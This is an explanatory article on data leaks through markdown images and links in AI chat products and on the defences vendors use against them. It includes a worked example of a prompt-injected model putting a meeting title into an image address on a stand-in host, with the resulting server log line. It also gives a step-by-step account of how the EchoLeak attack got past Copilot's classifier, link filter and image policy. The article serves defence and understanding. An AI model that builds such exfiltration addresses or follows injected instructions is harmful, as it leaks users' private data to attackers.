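# Blocking, proxying and validating images and links in AI chat interfaces

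## How a chatbot's reply can send data to an outside server

AI chat products such as OpenAI's ChatGPT and Microsoft's Copilot show a language model's answers as formatted text, with headings, tables, pictures and links. Every picture and link has a web address, which can contain data as well as a location. If an attacker gets the model to write a private detail into the address of a picture on the attacker's server, the user's browser sends that detail to the server when it loads the picture. Security researchers call this exfiltration, which means moving private data to someone who should not have it.

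The attacker usually uses prompt injection, which means placing text in an outside source, such as an email or web page, that the model follows as if it were an instruction. *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks* (Microsoft, 2025) notes that the text needs no special format. It can be in a plain text file, and white letters on a white background will hide it from a human reader. The attacker does not need access to the victim's account. The victim only has to ask the assistant to summarise a page or go through an inbox that contains the attacker's text.

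Researchers are still finding new cases. *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) described three ways an email could extract data from Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for office work, without the victim clicking anything. One of the three used an image address, according to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), and Microsoft had patched them all by mid-November.

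### From the model's text to the browser's request

A language model produces plain text. To get formatting out of it, chat products have the model write in markdown, a plain-text notation in which a few punctuation marks stand for headings, links and images. An image takes an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and an address in round brackets:

```
![A bar chart](https://pictures.example/chart.png)
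```

(No real website has an address ending in .example; the ending exists for use in documentation.)

The vendor's server sends this text to the user's browser or app, usually in small pieces while the model is still writing. There the renderer, the software that turns the model's text into what the user sees, recognises the pattern and translates it into HTML, the language of web pages:

```
<img src="https://pictures.example/chart.png" alt="A bar chart">
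```

This HTML element contains only the picture's address, so the browser connects to the host, pictures.example, and sends a GET request, the ordinary message browsers use to ask for pages and files. *Bing Chat*, a post on security researcher Johann Rehberger's blog Embrace The Red about a 2023 flaw in Microsoft's chatbot, describes the same steps from markdown to HTML to connection, all of which happen without any action by the user.

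Browsers load images on ordinary web pages the same way, which is mostly harmless because whoever built the page chose the image addresses. In a chat window, the model writes the addresses, and it has access to the user's conversation and perhaps their mail and files.

The outside server receives the whole address. The browser uses the host name to reach the server and sends the rest in the request. Encryption does not prevent the leak, because the outside server decrypts the request. The leak is complete once the request arrives, whether or not the server returns a picture. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out, so the attacker may need only a standard web server and its log file.

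### A worked example: a meeting title in a server log

Suppose an employee has an assistant that can read her email and open web pages. She asks it to summarise a page about conference venues and to check her inbox for the dates she needs. The page's author has added a passage, invisible to her, that asks any AI assistant to finish its answer with a small picture and to put the title of the reader's next meeting into the picture's address. The model takes the passage for part of its task. It finds an invitation called "Budget review" and ends an otherwise good summary with an image at this address:

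```
https://pictures.example/pixel.png?title=Budget%20review
```

| Part of the address | Name | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| `https://` | Scheme | Selects an encrypted connection |
| `pictures.example` | Host | Identifies the server that gets the request, here the attacker's |
| `/pixel.png` | Path | Identifies a file on that server |
| `?` | Separator | Marks where the parameters begin |
| `title=` | Parameter name | A label of the attacker's choosing |
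| `Budget%20review` | Parameter value | The private data, with `%20` standing for the space |

The renderer turns the line into an HTML image, the browser asks for the image, and the attacker's server adds a line to its log:

```
203.0.113.7 [05/Dec/2026:10:14:02 +0000]
"GET /pixel.png?title=Budget%20review HTTP/1.1" 200 "Mozilla/5.0 ..."
```

From left to right, the entry lists the network address the request came from, the time, the request itself, a status code (200 means the server returned the file) and the browser's description of itself. The meeting title is part of the request. If the picture is a single transparent pixel, the employee sees only a summary of conference venues.

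Real entries look much the same. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* reproduces one from September 2023 in which the parameter holds a complete link from a ChatGPT session, with its colons and slashes encoded as the space is above. *SearchLeak* (Taler, 2026) describes the closest match to the invented example. Researchers at the security company Varonis got Microsoft 365 Copilot to search a mailbox and put the title of an email into an image address, and the title then appeared in a log on their server. Email titles can be worth stealing because some contain login codes. The victim first had to open a prepared link to Copilot's own search page but did not have to click anything in the reply, and the browser sent its request before Copilot had finished writing. Microsoft has since patched the flaw.

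A URL parameter is the most convenient place to hide data, but Microsoft also lists the path and the subdomain (a prefix to the host name), and says attackers can encode the data so that it no longer looks like words. A filter that only searched addresses for suspicious parameters would therefore miss much of the data sent this way.

### Images leak on display, links leak on a click

The same address can also be put in a markdown link, which the renderer turns into clickable text. An ordinary browser sends nothing to the address until the user clicks the link, so this kind of leak is called one-click. An image leak is called zero-click because it happens when the reply appears on screen.

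EchoLeak, a flaw that Aim Security found in Microsoft 365 Copilot, exposed users' data first through a link and then through an image. Reddy and Gujral's *EchoLeak* (2025) reconstructs the attack. An attacker's email led Copilot to put sensitive details from the user's files into the address of a link. Copilot's filter for outside links missed it because the link used reference-style markdown, which defines the address separately from where it is used. The user still had to click the link. Changing it to an image removed the need for a click, but the attacker then had to get past another barrier in the browser. Aim Security reported the flaw privately, and Microsoft fixed it in May 2025 and said it had no evidence that anyone had used it in a real attack.

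Requiring a click offers some protection, because the user may ignore the link or notice something suspicious in its address, such as a client's name. But markdown lets a link's visible text differ from its address, so "click here" can hide a long string of stolen text. Some messaging apps also fetch a preview of every link they receive, and PromptArmor found that this leaks the data without a click.

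An image or link from an untrusted page can do harm even when it carries no private data. In May 2026 The Hacker News (2026) reported Permiso Security's finding that ChatGPT, after summarising a web page, would load images and display working links from that page. Permiso's main concern was phishing, because a fraudulent link looks more credible in an assistant's answer. Phishing is a different harm from exposing the meeting title in the log. An address copied unchanged from a public page contains nothing about the user. An address can pass on private data only if the model assembles it, or picks it from a set, in response to that data.

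### Why vendors act on the display

Stopping the model from following the attacker's text would be neater, and vendors try, but nobody has found a dependable way to do it. A model receives the user's request and the contents of the web page as one sequence of text, with no built-in separation between instructions and data. *The Framing Gap*, a 2026 study of agents that hold a secret while reading untrusted text, shows how much the wording of a rule can matter. A rule against disclosing the secret "in any form" reduced leaks from 31.9% to zero, but the rate was 48.8% with a rule that listed particular forbidden behaviours without that catch-all.

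In the same study, the ChatGPT product leaked data in none of 48 valid trials, although the same attacks succeeded up to 100% of the time against the model when developers called it directly. Zero leaks in 48 trials is still statistically compatible with a true leak rate of around 6%, and an attacker can reword the text and send it again. Simon Willison, a programmer who has collected such cases for years, writes in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* that in security "99% is a failing grade" because an attacker will look for the remaining 1%.

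Willison argues that a leak requires private data, exposure to untrusted content and a means of sending data out, and that the only reliable defence is to remove one of them. The first two are hard to give up. An email assistant, for example, has to read email, which is both private and untrusted. Willison therefore focuses on the means of sending data out, which is generally the easiest to remove. In a chat window, much of it consists of images that few users would miss.

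Microsoft similarly distinguishes two kinds of defence. A probabilistic defence, such as a classifier that looks for injected instructions, lowers the chance of a successful attack. A deterministic defence rules out a particular attack whatever the model does. Microsoft says it does not rely on blocking every injection. It gives the example of the markdown image leak, where the company blocked the route by which the data left after Rehberger reported the problem. The model can still write any address, but ordinary software, with no language model in it, controls whether anything is fetched.

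That guarantee has two limits. It doesn't stop the injection itself, so the attacker's text can still distort a summary, and an assistant with tools may be able to send data out through them. OpenAI claims only to prevent quiet leaks through the address itself. The guarantee also applies only to cases its rule covers. Copilot's link filter was deterministic too, and it failed against EchoLeak because nobody had written a rule for the other way of writing a link.

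### The discovery in spring 2023

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found the image leak in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023. In his attack, a script on a malicious website added instructions to any text a visitor copied, and the visitor then pasted it all into ChatGPT without reading it. The instructions asked ChatGPT for a transparent single-pixel image with data from the chat in its address. Samoilenko's *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* shows an outside server receiving a piece of code that ChatGPT had just corrected. It then shows a more persistent version, in which every later answer sent the user's latest question to the server.

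He acknowledged that the attack sometimes failed because ChatGPT's answers varied from one attempt to the next, and that passwords were much harder to extract than code or questions. He also described a link version, which leaked data only if the user clicked. He recommended that OpenAI not let ChatGPT reply with markdown images at all. The attack reached a wider audience on 14 April, when Willison (2023) called it "ingenious" in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*.

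SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* confirms that Rehberger found the same flaw independently a few days after Samoilenko. He reported it to Microsoft on 8 April 2023 and to OpenAI on 9 April. His versions of the attack didn't require the user to copy and paste anything. In Bing Chat, the attacker's text could be in a comment or an advertisement on the page the user had open, and in ChatGPT it could come in through a plugin, an add-on that fetched web pages or video transcripts for the model.

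Microsoft acknowledged the problem and told Rehberger on 15 June that it had a fix in place. (His 2026 retrospective, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates the fix to May, but the date he recorded at the time is probably more accurate.) OpenAI told him that markdown images were a feature and that it planned no changes, according to his post *ChatGPT Plugins*. It kept that position until December 2023, when ChatGPT's web version began checking with an OpenAI server that an image address was safe before loading it, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. In 2026 Rehberger wrote of dozens of such flaws across the industry.

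### Where a fix can sit

Between the model's last word and the attacker's log there are six places where a vendor can step in. In roughly the order in which a reply reaches them, they are:

1. The vendor's server, which has the model's text before the user's device does. It can remove an address or put a notice in its place, which is called link redaction, or run a sanitizer, a program that removes or neutralises dangerous elements before display.

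2. The renderer. It can decline to turn image markdown into an HTML image, and show the description, the bare address or a button instead. Each app may have its own renderer, and a fix in one does nothing for the others.

3. A URL safety check. Before loading anything, the app sends the exact address to the vendor's server, which answers yes or no. OpenAI chose this in December 2023.

4. The browser's own policy. A Content Security Policy (CSP) is a header, sent along with a web page, that tells the browser which hosts it may load images and other resources from. The list of permitted hosts is an allowlist, and the browser refuses everything else. Microsoft's 2023 fix for Bing Chat worked at least partly this way, with four Microsoft hosts on the list. In the worked example, the browser would have found that pictures.example was not among them and sent no request.

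5. An image proxy, a vendor's server that fetches the outside image and passes it to the user's browser. The outside server then deals with the vendor and never sees the user's network address. It still receives the full image address, meeting title included, unless the proxy also refuses some requests.

6. The click. For a link, the app can step in after the user presses it and before the browser goes anywhere, with a warning that displays the address. OpenAI's warning says that the link is unverified and may contain information from the conversation, and leaves the user to decide whether to open it.

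## Not loading images at all, or only after a click

The simplest fix is for the app never to request images, or to request one only after the user clicks to load it. Both approaches stop the zero-click leak, and neither needs software to judge whether an address is dangerous.

Vendors limit image loading in three ways. Some apps never render image markdown as a picture. Others show a button in its place and load the picture when the user clicks. Others show pictures by default but offer a setting that turns them off.

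The first two are changes to the renderer. In the example of the employee with the "Budget review" invitation, suppose the attacker's text had the model describe its picture as "Venue map". Instead of an HTML image element, a renderer with one of these fixes might produce one of the following:

```
Never load:    <span>Venue map</span>
Click first:   <button>Show image: Venue map</button>
```

Neither line gives the browser anything to fetch. With the button, the app stores the image's address and creates the image element only when the user clicks. Hiding the image with CSS would not work, because browsers usually fetch hidden images too.

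The rule should also apply at the last step, where the renderer would create the image element, because that covers every way of writing an image. A rule that matches only Markdown's usual exclamation mark and brackets can miss other forms, such as raw HTML, which many renderers accept, and reference-style images, which use a syntax like the one that got EchoLeak's link past Copilot's filter.

### Generative AI Studio: no images and no links

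Google chose the strictest version for Generative AI Studio, a part of its cloud service where developers try out models. As far as Rehberger could tell, the studio stopped turning images or links into HTML. Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI* describes how he had earlier got a model there to put a summary of the conversation into an image address, so that the summary reached his server. He reported the flaw on 30 August 2023. When he asked about it, Google confirmed on 19 October that it had fixed the problem, probably some weeks earlier.

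Blocking links as well as images also prevents the one-click leak. A user can still copy an address and open it, but is unlikely to do so by accident. Rehberger called this "probably the best possible fix" for security, especially in a product that does not need images or links. Developers testing a prompt lose little, because they mostly want to read the response text.

The danger was also smaller there than in an assistant that reads email, because the studio could not yet fetch outside content. The attacker's text had to be in something the user pasted in, or possibly in data used to train a custom model. Rehberger rated the flaw medium, and Google rated it high in impact but low in likelihood.

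Some vendors remove some or all images, even though people expect to see pictures in a general chat product. GitHub removed images from Copilot Chat, its programming assistant, and Google removes external images from Gemini's replies before display.

### Claude's "Show Image" button

Anthropic chose to have its chatbot, Claude, load images only after a click. Rehberger had found that a file uploaded to Claude could contain instructions to put the earlier conversation into an image address. According to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, he reported this on 12 July 2023, and Anthropic validated the report on 18 July and closed it on 26 July. From then on, users had to press a "Show Image" button to load a picture. Rehberger wrote that the fix "isn't perfect" and hoped for a better one, but he agreed that it stopped the automatic leak.

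Reddy and Gujral reach a similar view in a table that matches defences to the steps of EchoLeak. They credit human approval of outside content with stopping both the automatic image request and the zero-click leak. This is nearly true by definition, since a leak that requires a click is a one-click leak.

Requiring a click still makes an attack harder. Samoilenko's persistent attack leaked something with every answer, but if the app asked about each picture separately, the employee would have to click every time for the attack to work. A transparent single-pixel image also loses its main advantage, invisibility, because the app shows a button in its place. The employee might wonder why a summary of conference venues ends with a picture she did not ask for.

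The user is badly placed to decide whether to load the image. The risk lies in the image's address, but the user may see only a description that the model wrote under the attacker's influence. The attacker can choose an inviting description and have the model recommend looking at the image.

Displaying the address beside the button would help in this example, where the words "Budget review" are readable, but much less if the attacker had the model encode the title as a string of seemingly random characters. Harmless image addresses often contain such strings too, as file identifiers or access codes, so a user can infer very little from seeing one. Someone who presses the button several times a day for ordinary pictures will probably stop checking. After the press, the browser sends the whole address just as it would have without the button, unless the app has another check.

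The button also protected only the apps that had it. Willison (2024) quotes Rehberger's announcement that Anthropic had fixed an image leak in Claude's iOS app, well over a year after the first fix.

### Outside pictures in Claude in 2026

Anthropic does not mention the "Show Image" button in its current help pages on images, and Claude now has other ways to show pictures, including web search. According to Anthropic's *Enabling and using web search*, Claude can pick images from Bing search results and display them beside its answer, each with a link to its source. The chat has no separate switch for image results, but turning off web search also turns them off.

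Anthropic gives companies a separate control for image results. They are on by default for Team plans and off by default for Enterprise plans, where an account owner has to enable them, according to its *Use visual and interactive content on Team and Enterprise plans*.

These pictures reach the reply by a different path from the one Rehberger attacked. *Changes in the system prompt between Claude Opus 4.6 and 4.7* (Willison, 2026) includes a list of Claude's tools, obtained from the model itself, in which image search is a separate tool. The model uses the tool to search for pictures and chooses among the results, so it does not have to compose an address. An address that Bing has already indexed cannot have the title of the employee's meeting added to it.

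The search request goes to an outside service and could in principle contain something private. Anthropic says that it does not send users' prompts to Bing and that Claude turns them into generic search requests. If the model does this rewriting, an attacker's text might influence it, so the rewriting is not a firm guarantee of privacy. But the request goes to Microsoft, and an attacker would need some way of seeing it there.

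Anthropic's *Custom visuals in chat and Cowork* also describes charts, diagrams and interactive graphics that Claude builds in HTML inside the conversation, for example from an uploaded spreadsheet. These charts don't need images from an outside server, which removes one of the main drawbacks of blocking images. The feature is in beta and works on the web and in the desktop app but not on phones. Displaying HTML that a model wrote requires its own restrictions.

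Drawings cannot replace photographs. Anthropic's examples for image search include checking what a recipe should look like, finding photos of a product and identifying a plant. An app that blocked every outside image would lose these uses.

There is little evidence about images at other outside addresses. In *Image content blocks from tool results not rendered inline in assistant response*, the developer dzhurinskiy complained that Claude's website did not show a chart-making tool's output in the assistant's answers. The tool returned each chart both as image data and as a web address. Claude could see the chart and described it correctly, but the user could see it only by opening a collapsed panel, which most people never do. Giving Claude the address did not help, because the site did not display outside images in its answers.

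This is one user's bug report, and it does not establish that Anthropic had security in mind. It does show that image blocking can be broader than necessary. An image embedded as data in the reply is already on the user's device, so displaying it sends nothing to an outside server. A renderer could block images at outside addresses and still display embedded ones.

### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

OpenAI's Lockdown Mode is an optional setting that blocks much more than images. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) announced it on 13 February for managed Enterprise, Edu, Healthcare and Teachers accounts. On 4 June, OpenAI began extending it to personal accounts and to Business accounts that customers set up themselves. Personal users turn it on under "Security" in their settings. In a managed workspace, an administrator creates a Lockdown Mode role and assigns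 people to it.

OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the help page for the setting, lists what changes:

| Feature | In Lockdown Mode | What still works |
|---|---|---|
| Images in replies | ChatGPT may not show images or fetch them from the web | Uploading images and generating new ones |
| Web browsing | ChatGPT reads only stored copies of pages | Searching, though results may be old or missing |
| Canvas, a workspace for text and code | Users cannot allow code written there to use the network | Code that needs no network |
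| File downloads | ChatGPT cannot download files for data analysis | Analysing files that the user uploads |
| Deep research and agent mode | Off | None of either feature |

Each of these features can send a request to an outside server. If ChatGPT opens a live web page, the site's server receives the page's address, which can contain a meeting title just as an image address can. The address of a download can too, and code with network access can send whatever its author likes. Reading a stored copy of a page avoids the problem, as OpenAI explains, because no live request leaves the network OpenAI controls.

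OpenAI's wording on images is looser than the rest. It says ChatGPT "may not display images in regular responses", which leaves room for exceptions. The Decoder's *ChatGPT's new Lockdown Mode lets you disable web access and more* was firmer, reporting in June that ChatGPT would no longer show web images in regular responses.

The rules for apps, the outside services that users connect to ChatGPT, depend on the type of account. On personal and self-managed Business accounts, the mode blocks live access to apps and any action that changes something in them if the access or action conflicts with its protections. In managed workspaces, it does not turn off every app, because some companies depend on them, and administrators decide which actions to allow.

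OpenAI advises those administrators against any use of apps they do not trust. Even in a trusted app, it advises them not to let ChatGPT write anything unless they are sure an attacker will not see the result. Even with images blocked, an assistant that posts a private detail in a shared document leaks it to every outsider who can open the document.

The mode also doesn't affect network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. Personal users who need a live web page can switch the mode off for a single chat without changing the setting for the whole account. But ChatGPT is likely to read text from strangers in such a chat, which then has only the ordinary protections.

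OpenAI says that some risk of leaks may remain in this mode through apps, unforeseen combinations of features and new techniques. The mode also does not block an attacker's instructions, which can still arrive in an uploaded file or a stored web page and make an answer wrong.

This seems slightly at odds with the announcement, in which OpenAI said the mode "deterministically disables" certain features. The two statements are compatible if the guarantee covers each disabled feature but the list of features may be incomplete. The list did prove incomplete. The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reported a flaw in ChatGPT's HTML preview, since patched, that got around the restrictions. In March, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) described another flaw, also patched, that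 blocking images would not have stopped because it let data be sent out from the environment where ChatGPT runs code.

### Who needs Lockdown Mode

In February OpenAI said that Lockdown Mode "is not necessary for most users". It intended the mode for a small group with unusual security needs, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations. When the mode reached personal accounts in June, OpenAI's head of security, Dane Stuckey, said it was for people at higher risk because of who they are, what they work on or what data they handle. He wrote that the loss of features was worth it for them.

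Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, liked the design because it uses fixed rules to cut off the means of sending data out, which leaves no AI system for an attacker to fool. But he concluded that if strong protection requires this mode, a determined enough attacker may still be able to get data out of ChatGPT when the mode is off, as it is by default.

OpenAI's advice is about how likely a user is to face a serious attack, while Willison's is about what happens if one comes. He is almost certainly right about the consequences. OpenAI says Lockdown Mode is meant to reduce the risk of such leaks substantially, so it must think the default settings leave a substantial risk. The default settings do have some defences, since ChatGPT was already checking image addresses before Lockdown Mode existed.

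OpenAI's advice is harder to assess because the announcement doesn't include figures on how often attacks occur. OpenAI has also changed how it describes the threat. In June, according to The Decoder, OpenAI wrote on its help page that prompt injection "is not currently a major risk" but could grow. By early December, in its answer to the same question, OpenAI called it "a known security risk" and no longer played it down.

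Text hidden in a public web page reaches anyone who asks an assistant about that page, so the attacker does not have to pick victims in advance. This exposes ordinary users too, though they may have less worth stealing than executives and security teams, who are obvious targets for an attacker who chooses victims one by one.

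## Removing links and images from the reply before display

Blocking every image in a chat product removes the useful ones too, and blocking every link makes answers hard to check. Many vendors therefore use software that checks each address in the model's reply and removes only those that break a rule. The software must first find every address. EchoLeak, the best-known failure of this approach, began with addresses that Microsoft's software missed.

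### How a sanitizer edits a reply

In the worked example, the model ends a summary of conference venues with an image whose URL contains the title "Budget review". A sanitizer can process that reply in five steps.

1. It parses the markdown, which means turning the string of characters into a tree of paragraphs, links, images and so on:

```
reply
  paragraph
    text: "The three venues compare as follows."
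  paragraph
    image
      description: "Venue map"
      address: https://pictures.example/pixel.png?title=Budget%20review
```

2. It goes through the tree and collects every node that has an address. In plain markdown these are links and images. An app that accepts raw HTML has more of them, because a video can have an address for its preview picture and a form has one for the server that receives its contents.

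3. It resolves each address, which means working out where a browser would really go. In `https://venues.example@pictures.example/map.png` the host is pictures.example, because browsers treat anything between the slashes and the @ sign as login details. An address that starts with two slashes and no scheme also leads to an outside server.

4. It compares the resolved address with a rule.

5. It deletes the node, replaces it with a notice or keeps it. With a link, it can drop the address and keep the visible words, so that the sentence still makes sense.

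The app then builds its HTML from the edited tree, without the deleted picture.

The choice of rule in step 4 decides what still gets through:

| Rule | Effect on the image with the meeting title | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Remove every outside image | Removes it | Removes useful pictures too |
| Remove addresses on a list of dangerous sites | Keeps it if the attacker's site is new | Misses a site until someone has identified it |
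| Keep only addresses on an allowlist | Removes it | An allowed site may pass the request on to another server |
| Keep only addresses that were in the user's message or the sources | Removes it, because the model assembled the address | An attacker can supply many addresses for the model to choose from |

To apply the last rule, the vendor needs a record of every address in the user's message and in the pages, emails and files that the model read. The sanitizer has to match the full address exactly. If it compared only host names, the attacker's page could include an ordinary link to pictures.example, and the model could add the meeting title to the end of that link.

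### Searching the text for patterns

A quicker method is to search the model's text for anything that looks like a link, without building a tree. Programmers usually do this with a regular expression, a compact description of a text pattern. This one finds anything in square brackets followed directly by anything in round brackets:

```
\[.*?\]\(.*?\)
```

The pattern would catch the picture in the worked example, and a vendor could add it in minutes. But it sometimes removes too little or too much. Some web addresses, including many on Wikipedia, contain round brackets, and the pattern stops at the first closing bracket and leaves the end of the address behind. An answer about programming may include markdown as a code sample, and the pattern removes it even though the renderer would display it as harmless text.

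The more serious problem is that markdown has other ways of writing a link. In reference-style markdown, the writer puts a label where the address would go and defines the label on a separate line:

| | Inline | Reference-style |
|---|---|---|
| Link | `[Venue map](https://pictures.example/map.png)` | `[Venue map][map]` and, on its own line, `[map]: https://pictures.example/map.png` |
| Image | `![Venue map](https://pictures.example/map.png)` | `![Venue map][map]` and, on its own line, `[map]: https://pictures.example/map.png` |

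Inline and reference-style links produce the same HTML, and the reader never sees the line that defines a reference-style link's address. Under CommonMark, the most widely used specification of markdown, that line can come before or after the link, even many paragraphs away. If the second pair of square brackets is empty or missing, the link's visible words serve as the label. If a reply defines one label twice, the first definition counts, so a filter that checked only the last one could approve one address while the browser loaded another.

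### EchoLeak, step by step

Ravia's *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (2025) describes how Aim Security's researchers built a complete attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot using this second way of writing a link. Outsiders cannot use a company's Copilot, but they can email its employees. When an employee asks a question, Copilot searches her mailbox, files and chats for relevant material and gives it to the model with the question. The attacker's email therefore had to look relevant to something she was likely to ask.

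The researchers assumed that Copilot's search splits long texts into chunks and matches each chunk to the question separately, so they wrote one very long email. They gave its sections headings on everyday office subjects, such as employee onboarding and leave of absence, and repeated the same instructions under each. In their tests, Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various subjects, though Ravia gives no success rate.

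Microsoft's classifier was supposed to catch such emails, but the researchers got past it by addressing the instructions to the human recipient and never mentioning AI or Copilot. In the email, they asked for the most sensitive information available, whether from anything Copilot had retrieved or from earlier messages in the chat. They also wrote that the recipient must never refer to the email, for compliance reasons, so Copilot didn't name it as a source.

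The researchers still needed a way to get the information out. Copilot's filter removed links to outside sites before the user could click them and was meant to leave only safe ones, such as links to internal pages. The result depended on what the model wrote:

| What Copilot wrote | Link filter | Browser's image policy | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inline link to the attacker's server | Removed it | Did not apply | No leak |
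| Reference-style link to the attacker's server | Missed it | Did not apply | Leak on a click |
| Inline image on the attacker's server | Removed it | Not reached | No leak |
| Reference-style image on the attacker's server | Missed it | Blocked it | No leak |
| Reference-style image through SharePoint | Missed it | Allowed it | Leak on display, if the victim had joined the attacker's site |
| Reference-style image through Teams | Missed it | Allowed it | Leak on display |

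Copilot's web page had a Content Security Policy that allowed images from a long list of hosts. The list included SharePoint, Microsoft's service for internal websites and shared files, and Teams, its chat and meeting app. Each had a relay, a service that would fetch any address given to it. The researchers put the attacker's address, with the stolen information in it, inside the relay's address. The browser checked only the relay's address, which was on a Microsoft host, so it sent the request. The relay then sent a second request to the attacker's server.

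The SharePoint relay worked only if the victim was logged in to SharePoint and had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, which few people would do for a site they had never heard of. The Teams relay, which Reddy and Gujral describe as a preview service, needed no action from the victim. Extending the filter to cover reference-style markdown would have closed this route only if the filter also blocked the Teams address, which belonged to Microsoft.

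Aim Security built the attack and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. Reddy and Gujral date Microsoft's first repairs to April and the full fix to May. Microsoft made the fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. On 11 June Microsoft published an advisory (CVE-2025-32711) and Aim Security published its findings, which it had withheld until Microsoft fixed the flaw, according to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025).

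Reddy and Gujral also mention that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content before the model processes it. This removes an example that the model could copy into its reply. But a language model can write a reference-style link without an example, from a description in ordinary words, so a check on the reply is still necessary.

Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click flaw in a major AI application to cause concrete harm. He argues that earlier attacks either required the user to direct the chatbot to a malicious source or could leak only a narrow range of data. The image leaks of 2023 didn't need a click in the reply either, so whether EchoLeak was first depends on the definition. It differed mainly in its entry point, an email that could sit unopened in a mailbox until the employee asked Copilot about something else.

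### When the filter and the renderer disagree

EchoLeak's link got past Microsoft's filter because the filter treated a label in square brackets as ordinary text, while the renderer turned it into a link. Security researchers call this kind of mismatch a parser differential, and it can happen wherever one program checks text that another interprets. Ravia tested Copilot from the outside, so his results show what the filter missed but not whether it used a text pattern or an incomplete parser.

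A filter that looks for markdown brackets also misses bare addresses, which many renderers turn into links automatically. GitHub's version of markdown, which many other products use, does this for text that starts with "http://", "https://" or "www.".

A filter that looks for bare addresses must also end each one at the same character as the renderer. GitHub's rules leave out a full stop at the end of an address, and they include a final round bracket only if it matches an opening one in the address. If the filter stops at a different character, it checks one address and the user gets a link to another. If a sanitizer removes a link's formatting but leaves the address as plain text, an automatic linker that runs later will make the address clickable again.

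Raw HTML adds more ways to write an image or link. In 2024, an HTML image tag leaked data from Google AI Studio, as Embrace The Red's *Google AI Studio Data Exfiltration Now Fixed* describes. An attacker who doesn't know which form will work can try several at once, since only one has to get through. 0DIN's *Faking the Pipeline* describes a 2026 attack on Antigravity, Google's coding tool, in which the attacker used injected text to request the same image in five forms, including an HTML tag, an image inside a link and reference-style markdown.

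Even a filter that works on parsed HTML can miss an attack if its list of what to check is incomplete. The security company Escape found the same flaw in the customer chat features of two unrelated companies. Both used react-markdown, an open-source renderer, with an add-on that turns raw HTML in the model's text into page elements. React-markdown checks the addresses in a fixed list of HTML attributes, the named settings inside a tag. One attribute was not on the list because it holds an entire document instead of an address. Escape used that attribute to run its own code in the browser of anyone who opened the conversation.

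Escape recommends allowing only listed tags and attributes and removing everything else, because a list of forbidden ones fails once an attacker finds one that is missing from it. A filter for image addresses can fail in the same way, although leaking a meeting title is a different and usually lesser harm than running code.

The order of the steps also matters, because a sanitizer that runs before the HTML add-on checks only unparsed text, and the add-on creates the dangerous elements afterwards. Escape explains how developers make this mistake. A sanitizer at the end of the chain strips out the work of other add-ons, such as those that draw formulas or diagrams, so a developer moves it earlier until the formulas display again. This puts it before the HTML add-on, where it has no effect.

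Chat apps stream a reply piece by piece, so a sanitizer that waits for the finished text may run after the browser has already displayed some of it. In SearchLeak, the image request went out before Copilot's filter ran. A vendor can avoid this by holding back each link or image until its address is complete and checked, which adds a slight delay.

### Google's sanitizer for Gemini

On 13 June 2025, two days after the EchoLeak disclosure, Google said that EchoLeak's image leak was "not applicable to Gemini". Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) attributes this to Gemini's markdown sanitizer, which does not render images at outside addresses. The sanitizer would therefore drop the image in the worked example, whatever its address contained.

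Google treats links more leniently. It checks them using Safe Browsing, its service for identifying dangerous websites, and removes the suspicious ones. In Google's example, Gemini summarises an email thread in Gmail and replaces an unsafe address with "suspicious link removed". The notice also alerts the user to a problem in the thread.

A link that contained the meeting title would pass this check if pictures.example were a new site with no record of abuse. *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents*, by the software security company Checkmarx, points out that an attacker can set up a new domain. Checkmarx reported the one-click leak to Google on 5 October 2025. Google closed the report four days later as infeasible to fix and said that the risk was not severe enough to track as a security bug, so it leaves such links clickable by choice.

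Safe Browsing is a poor match for this problem because it assesses websites, while the leak depends on what the model adds to an address. Google distinguishes risky addresses that were already in outside material from harmful ones that arise when Gemini follows malicious instructions. A record of where each address came from would separate the two, since the link with the meeting title was in none of the sources. Neither Google's post nor its April 2026 follow-up describes such a record.

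Outside researchers have seen some filtering that Google did not mention. *The Trifecta*, from the security company Tenable, notes that links in Gemini's answers went through a google.com address first and that Gemini cut some suspicious answers short. Tenable assumed that replies would be filtered and looked for a way to get data out through Gemini's tools. One of the three flaws it reported was in the browsing tool, which can send a request without putting any link or image in the reply.

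According to Adversa AI's *Google Workspace Gemini Agent Security Risks*, a researcher got past the sanitizer itself by combining quirks in automatic linking with open redirects, which are pages on trusted sites that forward visitors to any address. Gemini then automatically loaded an image that leaked data from Google Workspace, Google's office software, and Google paid the researcher a reward. Adversa AI summarises someone else's work in a sentence or two and leaves out the steps, so it is not clear which rule failed. If the summary is right, Google's statement about EchoLeak holds for Aim Security's method but not for every zero-click image leak.

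In Google's follow-up, *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) writes that a central policy engine holds the settings for address sanitization, user confirmation and tool use. When a new attack appears, staff can change these settings faster than they could retrain a model. His list of quick repairs includes the "regex takedown", a rule based on a regular expression. Pattern matching works better here than for finding every link, because staff have already seen the attack and know what text to look for. An attacker who changes the wording or syntax may get past such a rule, so it is mainly a stopgap until a more general repair is ready.

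### Microsoft's account of its own defences

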